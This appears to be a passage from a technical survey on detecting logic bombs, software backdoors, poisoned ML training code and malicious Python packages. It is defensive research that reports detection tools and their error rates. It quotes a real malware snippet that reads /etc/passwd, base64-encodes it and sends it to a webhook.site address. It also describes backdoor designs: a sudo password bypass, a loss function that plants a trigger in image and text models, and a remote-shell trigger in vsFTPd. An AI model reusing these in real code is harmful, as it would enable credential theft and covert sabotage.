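A and B are the sets of sensitive functions that the two branches call. If one branch reads the location and opens a connection, and the other only opens a connection, they share one function out of two, so D is 0.5. If they share none, D is 1.

A *one-class support vector machine* then learns a boundary around normal examples and flags anything outside it. Samhi and colleagues trained it on 10,000 conditions from apps that no antivirus engine had flagged, so training required no examples of logic bombs.

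Difuzer's developers ran it on 10,000 malicious apps. The data-flow stage found about 17 conditions per app, and the anomaly detector reduced this to about one for every two apps. The developers inspected 102 of the flagged apps by hand. All but one contained a hidden operation that they considered suspicious, a precision of 99%, but only 30 contained a logic bomb. Difuzer also flagged 3.54% of 10,000 benign apps, slightly more than the 3.39% of malicious apps. An alarm is therefore almost no evidence that an app is malware. It is mainly useful for deciding which condition an analyst should read first, which was the developers' aim.

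Normal behavior also depends on the kind of app. In *Improving Logic Bomb Identification in Android Apps via Context-Aware Anomaly Detection*, Alecci, Samhi and colleagues sorted apps into 49 groups, in one version by their store descriptions, and trained a separate detector for each. Their new tool, Difuzer++, found a bubble-shooting game that checked which phone mast the user was near, a check that would be less surprising in a map app.

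Researchers inspected 51 flagged apps from a new set of 3,743 and found logic bombs in 30 (58.8%), compared with 6 of 46 (13%) for the original Difuzer. All these apps were already known to be malicious, so the share would be much lower in an unsorted collection. Nobody knows how many logic bombs either tool missed. Detectors can't be compared fairly without a known set of logic bombs to test against, so *TriggerZoo (2022)* provides a dataset of apps with automatically inserted ones.

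### Checking whether a trigger can break a rule

Another approach checks whether the program can ever do something forbidden, regardless of how suspicious its conditions look. *Detecting Ladder Logic Bombs in IEC 61131-3 PLC Programs using ESBMC-PLC+* (Dantas, Cordeiro and Junior, 2026) applies it to the small computers that control pumps and valves in factories. In each cycle, these computers read the sensors, run the program and set the outputs. The user supplies a rule, for example that two machines must never run together, and a solver searches for a sequence of sensor readings that breaks it. If the solver finds one, that sequence is the trigger. If there is none, the tool can sometimes prove that the rule holds for any number of cycles.

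The tool found 149 of 150 logic bombs in simulated water-treatment programs and raised no false alarms. It found only 49% in a later version of the collection, where some of the bombs used harder arithmetic, because the solver ran out of time. It also cannot detect malicious code that doesn't break any of the stated rules.

### Comparing behaviour before and after a change

Lily, which Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli (2026), in *Not In My Git Yard*, present, needs no rules about the program. It runs the versions from before and after a change and compares their *system calls*, the requests a program makes to the operating system, for example to open a file or start another program. The set of system-call types in one run is that run's *profile*. Lily works as follows:

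1. It runs the new version on inputs saved from earlier rounds of testing. The resulting profiles define the new version's typical behaviour.
2. It tests the new version for ten minutes with AFL++, a fuzzer that randomly alters inputs and keeps those that reach new parts of the code.
3. For each input that AFL++ keeps, it checks whether the profile exactly matches a typical one. If so, the input is safe.
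4. Otherwise, it runs the old version on the same input. If the profile is the same, the change did not cause the behaviour, and the input is safe.
5. If neither check clears the input, Lily raises an alarm.

In symbols, let P_new(x) and P_old(x) be the profiles of the two versions on input x, and let R be the set of saved inputs. Lily flags x if

P_new(x) ∉ {P_new(r) : r ∈ R} and P_new(x) ≠ P_old(x).

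One of the test cases was a real attack on vsFTPd, a file server. Attackers had replaced an official release with one that opened a hidden connection point whenever a username contained `:)`. Anyone who connected there could run commands with full control of the machine.

AFL++ eventually generates a username containing `:)` and keeps it because it reaches code that no earlier input reached. The server then makes a combination of system calls that none of the saved inputs produces, so the behaviour is atypical. The earlier release does not make that combination of calls for the same username, so the behaviour is also new, and Lily raises an alarm. Lily then looks for changed lines that ran on this input and led to the unusual calls. This narrows 1,407 changed lines in five files to seven lines in one file, which are enough for a reviewer to recognise a remote shell.

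Kokkonis and colleagues tested Lily on 13 open-source programs, running it 20 times on each change because fuzzing is random. They also measured the false alarms from each of the two conditions alone:

| | Commits | Releases |
|---|---|---|
| Backdoored changes tested | 13 | 50 |
| Runs that caught the backdoor | 90% | 83% |
| Safe changes tested | 432 | 50 |
| False alarms, atypical behaviour only | 14% | 20% |
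| False alarms, new behaviour only | 10% | 58% |
| False alarms, both conditions | 0.2% | 4.3% |

Requiring both conditions helps because a backdoor's behaviour is usually both new and rare, while either condition alone can flag harmless behaviour. If a release starts writing a log entry for every request, every profile is new, but the behaviour is typical because the saved inputs produce log entries too. A program may also have always started a helper process after one rare error. When the fuzzer first hits that error, the profile will look atypical, but the old version does the same thing.

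If the two conditions' false positives were independent, about 1.4% of runs on safe commits would meet both. The actual rate was much lower, partly because Lily requires the same input to meet both conditions. Even so, if only one commit in 10,000 were malicious, most alarms from a detector with these error rates would be false, as the earlier base-rate calculation showed.

The averages also hide a lot of variation. Of the 43 false alarms on releases, 40 came from two releases of libsndfile, a sound library, and Lily flagged both in every run. The detection rates are based on only 13 different backdoors, three of them from real attacks, and the 50 backdoored releases reuse these.

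An attacker can also try to stop the fuzzer from reaching the trigger. In a sample of 337 code changes, the tests could reach only about 32% of the changed lines on average, mostly because the projects' own test set-ups did not cover the rest. The attackers who put a backdoor in the compression library XZ Utils in 2024 used a cryptographic check that a fuzzer cannot realistically pass by guessing.

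An attacker could also make the malicious behaviour look typical by first adding a harmless version of the trigger, so that the project saves inputs that activate it, and adding the malicious code later. When the researchers planted 100 such inputs, detection fell to 54% for commits and 46% for releases. A stricter mode, which discards saved inputs whose profiles differ between the two versions, restored the original detection rates but raised false alarms to about 2.5% for commits and 18% for releases.

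### Triggers in training code

How these tools would perform on machine-learning projects is a matter of inference from their designs. A training script typically contains conditions like these:

```python
if torch.cuda.is_available():
    model = model.cuda()
if config.debug:
    train_data = train_data[:100]
if rank == 0 and step % 1000 == 0:
    save_checkpoint(model)
if step == 50_000:
    start_second_phase()
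```

All four conditions are ordinary, though each resembles a hidden trigger. The first checks the hardware, as malware does when looking for signs of an analyst's test machine. The second, a debug flag, makes the program behave differently under test than in a full run. The third holds in one process out of many and on one step in a thousand, and it guards code that writes files. The fourth compares a counter with a constant, much as a time bomb does.

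TriggerScope's rules cover only time, location and phone messages, so they would miss most of these conditions. A version that also tracked step counts and process numbers would probably flag a large share of harmless training scripts, since TSOpen raised so many alarms on time checks in ordinary apps.

Difuzer's features would make the checkpoint condition look abnormal compared with conditions in phone apps, because the script saves nowhere else and the branch that saves shares nothing with the branch that doesn't. Training the detector on other training scripts, as Difuzer++ does with similar apps, should remove many such alarms. But an upload in the same branch that steals the checkpoint would then look normal too.

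Lily would suit data-loading code better than full training runs. Its test programs included libraries that decode images and sound, a task similar to reading datasets. If an update made a data loader send out an access key when it read a certain file, the system calls would probably change. A full training run is much harder to test because fuzzing depends on many quick runs. A training script may take minutes just to load its data, and ten minutes of testing would rarely reach step 50,000.

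A more basic problem is Lily's assumption that any meaningful backdoor must make system calls, because a program can affect the outside world only through them. The assumption holds even for some backdoors that seem to change only a value. In *ROSA*, which describes an earlier fuzzing tool, Kokkonis, Marcozzi and colleagues (2025) give the example of `sudo`, a program that runs commands as another user. Their backdoor changes the result of the password check to "success" if the password is `let_me_in`. The backdoor's own code makes no system calls, but `sudo` then runs the command instead of printing an error, which changes the profile.

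A changed loss function may have no such effect. The training script still reads the same files, uses the same graphics processor and saves checkpoints at the same steps. The numbers in the checkpoint are different, but writing them takes the same types of system call. The yellow-square condition, which changes a label in memory, would also leave the profile unchanged. Kokkonis and colleagues limit ROSA to conventional software and list backdoors in machine-learning models as a separate problem.

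A tool could instead check that a suspect program gives the same outputs as a trusted earlier version, which Dantas and colleagues suggest as future work for industrial controllers. For a training script, this could mean comparing the outputs of the old and new loss functions on the same batches. The check would reveal the yellow-square attack only if one of the pictures had a yellow square in the right corner, and it would also flag every deliberate change a researcher made to the loss.

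## Experiments with altered training and evaluation code

Bagdasaryan and Shmatikov poisoned the loss functions of several models to test the attack, and other researchers have since built checks for faulty training code. All but one of the experiments below used real machine-learning code or training runs, but researchers tested most of the checks only on accidental faults.

### A loss that teaches two tasks

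Training adjusts a model's weights to lower the loss, so changing the loss can change what the model learns. In Bagdasaryan and Shmatikov's setting, the attacker can change only the code that computes the loss, not the optimizer, architecture or learning rate. The attacker never sees the training data, the training run or the finished model.

The resulting model has to do two tasks:

- Main task: for an ordinary input x with the correct label y, it answers y.
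- Backdoor task: for an input x* that contains the trigger, it answers y*, a label the attacker chose.

Write θ(x) for the model's scores on x, and L for the formula that compares scores with a label. The altered code returns

ℓ = α₀ · L(θ(x), y) + α₁ · L(θ(x*), y*)

The coefficients α₀ and α₁ are nonnegative and add up to 1. In the clothing example, x might be a picture of a coat labeled "coat", and x* the same picture with a small mark, labeled "sandal". The optimizer receives only the sum, so it improves the model on both tasks.

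If the main loss is 0.5, the backdoor loss is 2.0, and their coefficients are 0.8 and 0.2, the code returns 0.4 + 0.4 = 0.8 instead of 0.5. Someone who doesn't know that the loss should be 0.5 would see nothing wrong with 0.8.

The attack barely affected the main task, so a developer who measured only accuracy on clean test data would not have noticed it. On ImageNet, a standard collection of photographs in 1,000 classes, one model's accuracy was 69.1% both before and after Bagdasaryan and Shmatikov trained a backdoor into it. The backdoored model gave the attacker's label to 99% of the images that contained a nine-pixel pattern. The accuracy of a model that rates film reviews fell from 91.4% to 91.3%, but it rated 98% of reviews containing a chosen name as positive, up from 53%.

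### What a reviewer could notice

The altered code is still visible in the repository. An ordinary training step runs the model forward once (line 7 of the ten-line loop) and backward once (line 9). The altered loss adds a forward pass for the extra inputs and backward passes to compute the coefficients. A reviewer could therefore look for loss code that runs the model again, creates new inputs and labels, or computes gradients itself. On line 8, `loss_fn` receives only scores and labels, so a new version that also takes the model as an argument would stand out.

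Legitimate projects do these things too. In fairseq and Transformers, the loss code has access to the model. Adversarial training alters inputs and runs the model on them, and distillation runs a second model to supply the labels. A rule against extra forward passes would flag both methods.

The altered run is also slower and uses more memory. Bagdasaryan and Shmatikov point out that this helps a team detect the change only if it knows how much time and memory its training normally takes with its own hardware and settings. Batch size alone greatly affects both, and many popular frameworks have no published baselines for comparison.

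Bagdasaryan and Shmatikov examined the automated tests in fairseq, Transformers and fast.ai and found that they gave little protection. The tests checked the shape of the loss but not its value. A loss is usually a single number, so 0.5 and 0.8 would both pass. Exact values are hard to test because results on graphics processors vary with hardware and randomness. The survey is several years old, so the projects may have better tests now.

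### A signed computation graph

PyTorch records the operations that lead to the loss in a *computation graph*, which it uses to compute gradients. In an ordinary step, the graph contains one path through the model. The altered loss adds a second path for the backdoor inputs, which joins the first where the code adds the two loss terms.

Bagdasaryan and Shmatikov propose using this difference as a defence:

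1. An expert builds the graph from clean training code and checks it.
2. The developers sign the graph and publish it with the model's code.
3. At every training step, the program compares the graph attached to the current loss with the signed one and requires an exact match.

Occasional comparisons could miss the altered code, which can implant a backdoor even if it acts on only some steps. Counting the loss functions in the graph could also miss it, because the attacker's code can compute a loss without calling a loss function.

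The defence assumes that the attacker can change only the loss code and cannot tamper with the signed graph. Someone with write access to the whole repository could delete the comparison. Bagdasaryan and Shmatikov know of no efficient way for loss code to update the model and preserve its accuracy without changing the graph, but they do not prove that none exists.

They built a prototype and showed the two graphs for one image model, but did not measure a false positive rate. The rate could be high in a research project, because researchers often change their loss functions and every honest change would need a new review and signature. A network that skips layers at random, like the one PyTea had to simplify, has no single correct graph.

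The graph also stays the same if an attack changes only the data or the random numbers. For example, the engineer's yellow-square condition swaps a label before line 8 runs, so the operations that follow are normal.

### Recomputing the loss

Checking a loss value requires a trusted reference value. *Plumbline* (Wen, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that Amazon uses to validate language-model training before long runs. The correct loss is the average cross-entropy over the tokens the model is supposed to learn. The system takes the model's raw scores from the training framework, computes this average separately at high precision, and compares it with the framework's loss. It checks the optimizer's update to the weights in a similar way. Where a tolerance might hide a fault, the system plants that fault in a copy of the data and passes the run only if the check detects it.

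In the earlier example, the recomputed loss would be 0.5 and the framework's would be 0.8. Wen and colleagues did not test a poisoned loss, but a mismatch that large should fail the check. Code that stayed inactive until later in the run would escape an earlier check.

Another check compares the gradients from one training step, g, with gradients from an independent implementation of the model, g_ref:

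s = ‖g − g_ref‖ / ‖g_ref‖

The double bars mean the length of a list of numbers, which is the square root of the sum of their squares. If g_ref is (3, 4) and g is (3, 4.5), the difference has length 0.5 and g_ref has length 5, so s is 0.1. The step fails if s is more than four times the noise measured by repeating the same run and by using less precise arithmetic. With noise of 0.02, the limit would be 0.08 and this step would fail. The margin is narrow in practice, since s reached 3.44 times the noise in steps with no known defect and was as low as 4.35 times the noise in the faulty steps that the check caught.

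In September and October 2026, the system found 61 problems across 13 combinations of framework and model. Of these, 32 were silent, meaning that training continued without an error message and the loss still fell. At least 16 of the silent problems occurred in runs that passed checks for stable training.

In one case, the code that loaded gpt-oss-20b, an OpenAI model with public weights, swapped the rows and columns of some weight matrices. The matrices were square, so their shapes stayed the same and a shape checker could not have detected the swap. The loss started at 17.08 instead of 1.48, but it fell during training and the run passed.

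The method needs an independent reference implementation. DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash had no suitable one, so the gradient check produced no result for its layers. A research project that invents a new loss has the same problem until someone separately writes a second implementation of the formula. Even then, the comparison would catch only code that departs from the formula and would miss a harmful term in the formula itself.

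### Judging a run by its curves

Developers without a reference usually watch how the loss changes over time, but this can fail. *TTrace* (2025), which presents a tool for checking training spread over several processors, describes a faulty program whose loss and gradient sizes stayed close to those of the correct one for many steps.

*Deep4ge* (Jahan, 2026) measured how much a fuller set of readings reveals about faults in training programs. It took 59 programs from Stack Overflow, repaired them, and planted faults using 27 kinds of edit, such as a wrong loss function or a bad learning rate. This produced 9,845 faulty runs and 4,382 correct ones. After each epoch, or pass through the training data, the programs recorded 30 values, including measures of accuracy, loss, gradients and memory use.

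A classifier that used only the final epoch had an AUROC of 0.649 on programs it had not seen before. Using the whole run raised this to 0.716, which is still too low to rely on. Most runs in the collection are faulty, so a classifier that called every run faulty would have an F1 score of 0.818, only slightly below the 0.825 of the classifier that used the whole run.

A poisoned loss would probably be harder to detect than these faults. Jahan retrained each altered program 15 times and kept it only if its accuracy differed from the original's by a statistically significant and reasonably large amount. A backdoor that left accuracy at 69.1% would not have met that condition, so the collection excludes changes like Bagdasaryan and Shmatikov's.

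### Rules learned from healthy runs

A fault can be obvious in the individual steps of training long before it affects the curves. Jiang, Zhou and colleagues (2025), in *Training with Confidence*, present TrainCheck, a tool that learns *invariants*, which are rules that should hold throughout training. It learns them from programs that developers believe to be correct, such as official examples, and then checks other programs against them:

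1. TrainCheck wraps the library's functions so that every call leaves a record. It also records changes to the model and the optimizer.
2. It fills in general templates using these records. One template requires certain calls to happen in a given order, another requires one event to happen during another, and another requires two values to stay equal. For the ten-line loop, candidate rules might include "`zero_grad` comes before `backward`" and "the weights change during `optimizer.step()`".
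3. It tests each candidate rule on the records and separates the cases where the rule held from those where it failed.
4. If a rule sometimes failed, the tool looks for a condition that distinguishes the two groups. This becomes the rule's *precondition*. If it finds none, it discards the rule.
5. During a new run, it records only what the chosen rules need and reports any violation.

The fourth step matters because many rules apply only to part of a model. In 2022, Hugging Face trained BLOOM, a large language model, on 384 graphics processors. The training software split the large layers across processors but gave each processor a full copy of some small layers. A bug made these copies diverge, and no one noticed for ten days.

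The candidate rule "weights are equal on different processors" failed 38 times for every time it held, because layers split across processors are supposed to have different weights on each. A tool that kept only rules that were usually true would have discarded it. TrainCheck found that the rule held for layers that are not split, which it identified by the setting `tensor_model_parallel` being false, and limited the rule to those layers. In a small reproduction of the BLOOM bug, the limited rule caught the problem one training step after it began.

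Jiang and colleagues reproduced 20 real silent errors, ranging from a forgotten `zero_grad` to a faulty hardware driver. TrainCheck caught 18 of them, each within one step of the cause taking effect. Detectors that monitored the loss, accuracy and gradient sizes together caught two, and a shape checker with constraints like PyTea's caught one. TrainCheck missed a run that ended early because the program had miscounted its steps, and a bug that affected only checkpoint saving. It also helped the researchers find six previously undiagnosed bugs.

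They measured false alarms on 63 programs with no known bugs. The false positive rate was below 2% when the tool learned from five or six similar programs, and below 5% with two or three. These figures seem to be the share of rules that raised a false alarm. If so, a correct run checked against 100 rules could still violate one or two of them. One faulty run produced 100 violations, of which 52 pointed to the fault. The others mostly reflected harmless differences from the example program, such as a function that the new model had no reason to call.

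The checks usually added less than 2% to the training time, although very small programs took up to 1.6 times as long.

All 20 errors were real bugs, and Jiang and colleagues did not test deliberate tampering. Like SpecDetect4ML, TrainCheck would probably detect the deletion of line 6 by an attacker. A poisoned loss is different because the program still clears the gradients, computes new ones and updates the weights in the right order. TrainCheck stores short fingerprints of tensors instead of their contents, so it can check whether two tensors are equal but not whether a loss should be 0.5 or 0.8. A rule about how often the model runs might happen to catch the extra forward pass, but this is untested. If TrainCheck learned its rules from earlier runs of the same project that already contained the poisoned loss, it would treat that loss as normal.

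### Comparing the code with the paper

A research paper often states what its code is meant to do, so a reviewer can look for mismatches between the two. *SciCoQA* (Baumgärtner and Gurevych, 2026) collects 635 mismatches to test whether language models can find them. 92 are real cases from GitHub discussions and published attempts to reproduce results, and GPT-5 created the other 543 by editing research code. In one real case, the paper computes two values and uses them to scale and shift a layer's output, but the code first maps both values into the range 0 to 1. About 24% of the real mismatches concern the loss.

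The researchers gave 22 models a paper with its code and asked for a list of mismatches. The two best models, Gemini 3.1 Pro and GPT-5 Mini, each found 43 of the 92 real cases, or 46.7%. Models did worse on longer inputs. They had the most trouble with steps that are in the code but missing from the paper, such as an undisclosed loss term. Everything a paper describes should be in the code, but a paper can leave out many of the code's details, so the model has to judge which omissions matter.

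*Dude* (Liu, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) addresses this by having some AI agents look for a paper's claims in its code and others look for the code's important steps in the paper. A simple version of this two-way search found more mismatches but also reported a lot of trivial set-up code, so *Dude* filters out code that has little to do with the paper's claims. Its agents also go back to the paper when a claim is vague, so that they do not invent details and then report them as missing. The table gives the results for GPT-5.4 on the 92 real cases.

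| Method | Recall | Precision |
|---|---|---|
| One model | 58.7% | 91.5% |
| Several agents, without the added safeguards | 75.0% | 74.2% |
| Dude | 80.4% | 93.7% |

A language model matched the reports to the known cases, and the precision figures leave out valid mismatches that were not on the original list. Liu and colleagues also ran Dude on 20 recent conference papers. It reported 48 mismatches, of which 45 were valid.

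That is more than two real mismatches per paper, in work that nobody suspected of sabotage. Baumgärtner and Gurevych list several innocent causes, such as simplified explanations, later updates to the code, and different people writing the paper and the program. A mismatch is therefore a good reason to ask the developers about it, but weak evidence of tampering. Neither study tested disguised changes, and an attacker who can edit the project's documentation could describe the added step as part of the method.

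### Recognising a flawed experiment

Code can match its paper exactly and still run an experiment that does not support the paper's claim. *Tampered ML* (Ebadian, Alamdari and colleagues, 2026) tested whether language models can recognise such experiments. It used written experiment designs rather than code, so its results do not show how well a model would find the same flaw in a repository.

The benchmark has 1,858 pairs of designs. One design in each pair describes an experiment from a published machine-learning paper, and the other is a copy with one planted flaw. A typical design is about 1,050 words, and the edit changes 2% of the text. The most common flaw, found in 20.5% of the pairs, is changing something else along with the method under test, which leaves two possible explanations for the result. Test data leakage is the flaw in 2.8% of the pairs.

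Each model judged every pair twice, with the designs in opposite orders, and got credit only if it chose the sounder design both times. Random guessing would succeed on 25% of pairs, and Anthropic's Opus 5 succeeded on 77.9%. The order had a large effect on some models. The older Opus 4.6 was right in about 66% of individual comparisons but chose correctly in both orders for only 43% of pairs. Models sometimes chose the flawed design because it was more detailed or followed common practice.

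The score partly reflects how Ebadian and colleagues built the benchmark. They removed pairs that several models had already solved, which made the remaining set harder. They also estimated from a human review that 86% of the pairs were valid, so some answers marked wrong may be defensible.

In another respect, the task was easier than a real review because the model always had a sound version to compare with. In April 2026, researchers who had auditors judge machine-learning codebases one at a time reported a best AUROC of 0.77. The auditors were often suspicious of code that was odd but honest. *Auditors Struggle to Catch Sabotage In End-to-End Transcripts of AI Safety Research* (Shenoy, Zang and colleagues, November 2026) reported an AUROC of 0.59 for human auditors and about 0.74 for the best AI models.

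## Scanners tested on labelled malicious Python packages

Most known malicious packages steal passwords or download another program, often during installation. These attacks are cruder than subtle sabotage of an experiment. Researchers have collected thousands of these packages, which has made package scanners the most developed tools for finding malicious code in a project's dependencies. Machine-learning projects need such tools because they can depend on thousands of packages. Most of the tests below used general Python packages, and only one measured false alarms on packages related to machine learning.

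### One matching rule is enough

The simplest scanners have a list of rules and flag a package if any of them matches. Guo, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *Cutting the Gordian Knot*, express this as a formula:

is_malicious(p) = match(r₁, p) ∨ match(r₂, p) ∨ … ∨ match(r_k, p)

Here p is the package, r₁ to r_k are the rules, and ∨ means "or". A rule might look for a web address, a call that starts another program, or encoded text. Bandit4Mal, a version of Bandit adapted to detect malware, has 45 rules that search the syntax tree. OSS Detect Backdoor, part of Microsoft's OSSGadget collection, has 41 rules that search every text file. GuardDog, from the software company Datadog, combines code rules with checks on a package's metadata, such as its name.

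Adding a rule to such a list cannot reduce false alarms, because no rule can cancel another's match. Suppose each rule matches 2% of legitimate packages, independently of the others. Then k rules together flag 1 − 0.98ᵏ of legitimate packages, which is about 8% for four rules and 60% for 45. Large legitimate packages are more likely to be flagged, because every extra file gives each rule another chance to match.

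*A Benchmark Comparison of Python Malware Detection Approaches* (Vu, Newman and Meyers, 2022) tested three scanners on 168 malicious packages, 1,430 popular ones and 986 others chosen at random. One scanner was PyPI's set of four rules for `setup.py`, a file that can run code during installation. The table shows the share of packages that set off at least one alert.

| Scanner | Files scanned | Malicious | Popular | Random |
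|---|---|---|---|---|
| PyPI checks (4 rules) | `setup.py` | 58.9% | 33.2% | 14.9% |
| | all Python files | 85.7% | 94.2% | 67.8% |
| OSS Detect Backdoor (41 rules) | `setup.py` | 50.6% | 41.7% | 33.1% |
| | all Python files | 85.1% | 96.6% | 77.2% |
| Bandit4Mal (45 rules) | `setup.py` | 66.7% | 79.5% | 70.2% |
| | all Python files | 90.5% | 96.6% | 84.6% |

When all Python files were included, every scanner flagged popular packages more often than malicious ones. The popular packages averaged about 115 Python files, compared with eight for the malicious ones.

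Requiring several alerts before flagging a package did not solve the problem. OSS Detect Backdoor raised 124,267 alerts for one popular package, whereas the PyPI checks never raised more than three for a malicious package's `setup.py`. A higher threshold therefore misses malicious packages while still flagging many legitimate ones.

### What registry administrators would accept

In 2022, Vu and two colleagues also interviewed two people from PyPI's maintainer community and an academic security researcher. (Vu and the same colleagues published another paper on the subject, *Bad Snakes*, in 2023.) Each week, PyPI was receiving about 20,000 new releases and its administrators were removing about 20 malicious packages. An administrator was willing to spend about 20 minutes a week on malware reports, and the real cases alone would take up all of that time at a minute each.

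The administrators considered even a false positive rate of 0.01% too high, although it would mean only two false alarms a week. The researchers suggested a limit of 0.001% for scanning packages after publication, and a lower limit for a scanner that blocks uploads. A scanner that flagged 15% of releases would raise about 3,000 alarms a week. PyPI had introduced its own checks in 2020 and disabled them two years later.

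The administrators worried less about missed attacks because they mainly wanted to remove crude and frequent ones. They relied on outside researchers, who ran their own scanners, filtered out the false alarms and reported the rest. A machine-learning team that scans its own dependencies has far fewer packages to check, but many of them are popular libraries, which set off the most alarms.

### Using the order of operations

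Guo and colleagues designed PyGuard to consider the order in which code does things. They illustrate the need for this with two packages that make similar calls. The malicious one, `gmgeoip`, does roughly this:

```python
accounts = open("/etc/passwd").read()
encoded = b64encode(accounts.encode())
body = urlencode({"data": encoded}).encode()
urlopen("https://webhook.site/...", body)
```

It reads the computer's list of user accounts, converts it to base64 (a way of writing any data as plain text), and sends it to an outside address. The harmless package, `gen_wrappers`, contains code like this:

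```python
port = os.environ.get("PORT_CMFY", 8889)
query = urlencode({"filename": filename})
reply = await client.get(f"http://localhost:{port}/view?{query}")
return b64encode(reply.content).decode()
```

This code fetches a picture from a server on the same computer and returns it as base64 text. The name `PORT_CMFY` suggests the server runs ComfyUI, a program for generating images with AI models. Bandit4Mal, OSSGadget and GuardDog all flagged this package, mainly because they treated its web address as a suspicious link.

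The developers prepared PyGuard in four steps:

1. They ran four rule-based scanners on 18,137 packages, about half of them malicious. GPT-4.1, an OpenAI language model, extracted the code around the flagged lines, including the statements those lines depended on.
2. GPT-4.1 described each operation in a few words, and three experts merged the descriptions into 327 types of action. Calls to different libraries that do the same thing count as one type.
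3. They converted the code into sequences of actions. This produced 2,431 sequences with an average of 4.2 actions each.
4. They used PrefixSpan, an algorithm that finds common subsequences, to look for patterns that separate malicious sequences from benign ones.

In simplified form, the two examples become:

- `gmgeoip`: read file → encode as base64 → send web request
- `gen_wrappers`: read environment variable → send web request → encode as base64

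A subsequence keeps the order of the actions but may skip some. "Encode, then send" is a subsequence of only the first example, and "send, then encode" is a subsequence of only the second.

A pattern is *deterministic* if it occurs only in malicious sequences or only in benign ones. PrefixSpan first looks for patterns shared by at least 30 sequences. The program then sets aside the sequences that contain a deterministic pattern and repeats the search with lower minimums, down to two sequences. From the remaining sequences, it collects *justifiable* patterns, for which at least 90% of the matching sequences belong to one class. A final step removes redundant patterns, leaving 278 deterministic and 26 justifiable ones.

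Patterns found in only two sequences are weak evidence, since they may be missing from the other class by chance. The order of operations alone can also mislead, because a program that sends a photograph to an online vision model may read a file, encode it as base64 and send a web request, just as `gmgeoip` does. The two programs differ in which file they read and where they send its contents.

PyGuard therefore passes unclear cases to a language model. It scans each file of a new package as follows:

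- If the file matches a deterministic malicious pattern, PyGuard flags it, even if it also matches a benign one.
- If it matches only deterministic benign patterns, PyGuard clears it.
- Otherwise, PyGuard retrieves the most similar benign and malicious examples and gives them to the language model. For a justifiable pattern, it adds a written rule for telling the two apart. One such rule treats encoding system files as suspicious and encoding a user's documents as harmless.

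One flagged file is enough to flag the whole package.

Guo and colleagues argue that an attacker cannot evade PyGuard by adding harmless actions, because the malicious subsequence would still be there. This is true for malicious patterns PyGuard already has, but a new kind of attack that matched none of them could apparently evade detection by including a benign pattern, since PyGuard would clear the file without querying the language model.

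### PyGuard's results and the limits of balanced datasets

The main test used 4,757 packages that the developers had kept out of the pattern search, 2,394 benign and 2,363 malicious.

| Scanner | False alarms | Malicious packages missed |
|---|---|---|
| PyGuard | 2 | 19 |
| GPT-4.1 alone | 115 | 34 |
| GuardDog | 141 | 101 |
| Bandit4Mal | 1,927 | 1,080 |
| OSSGadget | 2,000 | 244 |
| PyPI checks | 2,117 | 17 |

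The paper's summary compares PyGuard's two false alarms with 1,927 to 2,117 for existing tools, but that range leaves out GuardDog's much lower count. Some of the paper's percentages do not match its counts, so small differences between scanners mean little.

PyGuard's advantage was clearest on packages that the researchers had run through an obfuscation tool, which renames variables and disguises text. GPT-4.1 alone raised 637 false alarms on the 1,019 benign packages in this test, compared with 25 for PyGuard. The stored patterns seem to matter more than model size. The smaller GPT-4.1 mini, given the same patterns, raised only nine false alarms and missed 13 malicious packages in the main test.

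On a set of more recent packages, PyGuard raised five false alarms among 1,001 benign packages, or 0.5%. Half of the packages in these tests were malicious, compared with roughly one in 1,000 PyPI releases in 2022, so the base-rate problem described earlier applies. At that false-alarm rate, PyPI's 20,000 weekly releases would have produced about 100 false alarms, compared with about 20 malicious releases.

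Copied attacks can make such a test easier too. Attackers often publish the same malicious code under many names, and Guo and colleagues found only 2,283 distinct malicious snippets in 8,543 packages. Unless the developers kept all copies of each attack on the same side of the split, PyGuard may have learned its patterns from copies of many of the test attacks.

Scans of new uploads avoid the artificial balance, but they do not show how many attacks a scanner missed. PyGuard flagged 233 of 8,249 new packages between March and June 2024, and PyPI confirmed 219 of them as malicious. GPT-4.1 did not exist yet, so that run must have used a different model. *MalGuard* (2025) describes a scanner that flagged 144 of 64,348 packages, and 113 of those flagged were malicious. The 31 false alarms give a false positive rate of about 0.05%, five times the rate that PyPI's administrators had considered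 too high. Of these, 25 were test demos that made web requests or started processes, and the other six were pranks. *PyFEX* (2026) reports that its scanner flagged 222 packages over 90 days, of which 212 were malicious.

### Asking a language model what the code does

*An Evaluation of Large Language Models for Detection of Malicious Python Packages* (Ryan, Khalil and colleagues, 2026) tested 13 models on detecting malicious packages and on identifying what those packages do wrong, which a reviewer who receives an alarm also needs to know.

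For the first task, each model judged whether files were malicious. The test used 103 files, ten of them malicious, with five prompt styles and up to three randomness settings. Average F1 scores ranged from 0.40 for the small Gemma 3 4B to 0.99 for GPT-4.1. The models missed few malicious files, but in about half of the combinations of model and settings, most of the files they flagged were harmless. The average F1 was 0.74 for a plain question but only 0.23 when the prompt included worked examples. These scores are rough because, with only ten malicious files, a single miss lowers recall by ten percentage points.

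For the second task, the models had to name the malicious behaviours in 370 packages, choosing from 47 types. People had already marked the relevant lines, but the researchers scored only whether a model named the right types, so the results do not show how well a model can locate those lines. The models did much worse than on the first task. With the best settings, the average F1 was 0.91 for the verdict, 0.75 for the broad category of behaviour and 0.52 for the specific type. Only 0.3% of answers listed exactly the right types, although 92% included at least one correct type.

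Many errors came from treating ordinary operations as malicious. The models often reported normal download commands as "payload droppers", code that fetches a harmful program. Only 16% of their payload-dropper reports were correct. The models also missed 97% of cases where code chose a module to import while running, and 81% of cases where it suppressed error messages. Some human labels were wrong too. In one package, the label pointed to a remote-control command that was commented out and would never run, while the model reported a different command that would run.

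Ryan and colleagues recommend using language models to choose packages for human review, but not to explain what a package does. Their results may not apply to large machine-learning libraries, because the benign packages in their test had at most 260 lines and the models were worse at identifying behaviours in longer packages.

### Agents that investigate a package

*CHASE* (Toda and Mori, 2026) divides the analysis of a package among three AI agents. A supervisor plans the investigation and revises the plan after each result. A second agent decodes hidden code, and a third looks up web addresses and downloads whatever the package would fetch.

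One package, `libstrreplacecpu`, contained a base64-encoded command for PowerShell, a Windows tool for running commands. The decoding agent found a Dropbox link in the command. The supervisor passed the link to the web agent, which found that seven security vendors had flagged it as malicious. The system uses ordinary programs to handle long random strings, such as file hashes, because language models tend to make mistakes when copying them.

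The test used 500 malicious packages and 2,500 recent benign packages chosen at random. In one run, CHASE identified 492 of the malicious packages and timed out on the other eight. It raised two false alarms among the 2,475 benign packages it finished, a rate of 0.08%. CHASE classified all the unfinished packages correctly within three attempts. The median analysis took four and a half minutes, so Toda and Mori suggest running CHASE only on packages that a faster scanner has flagged.

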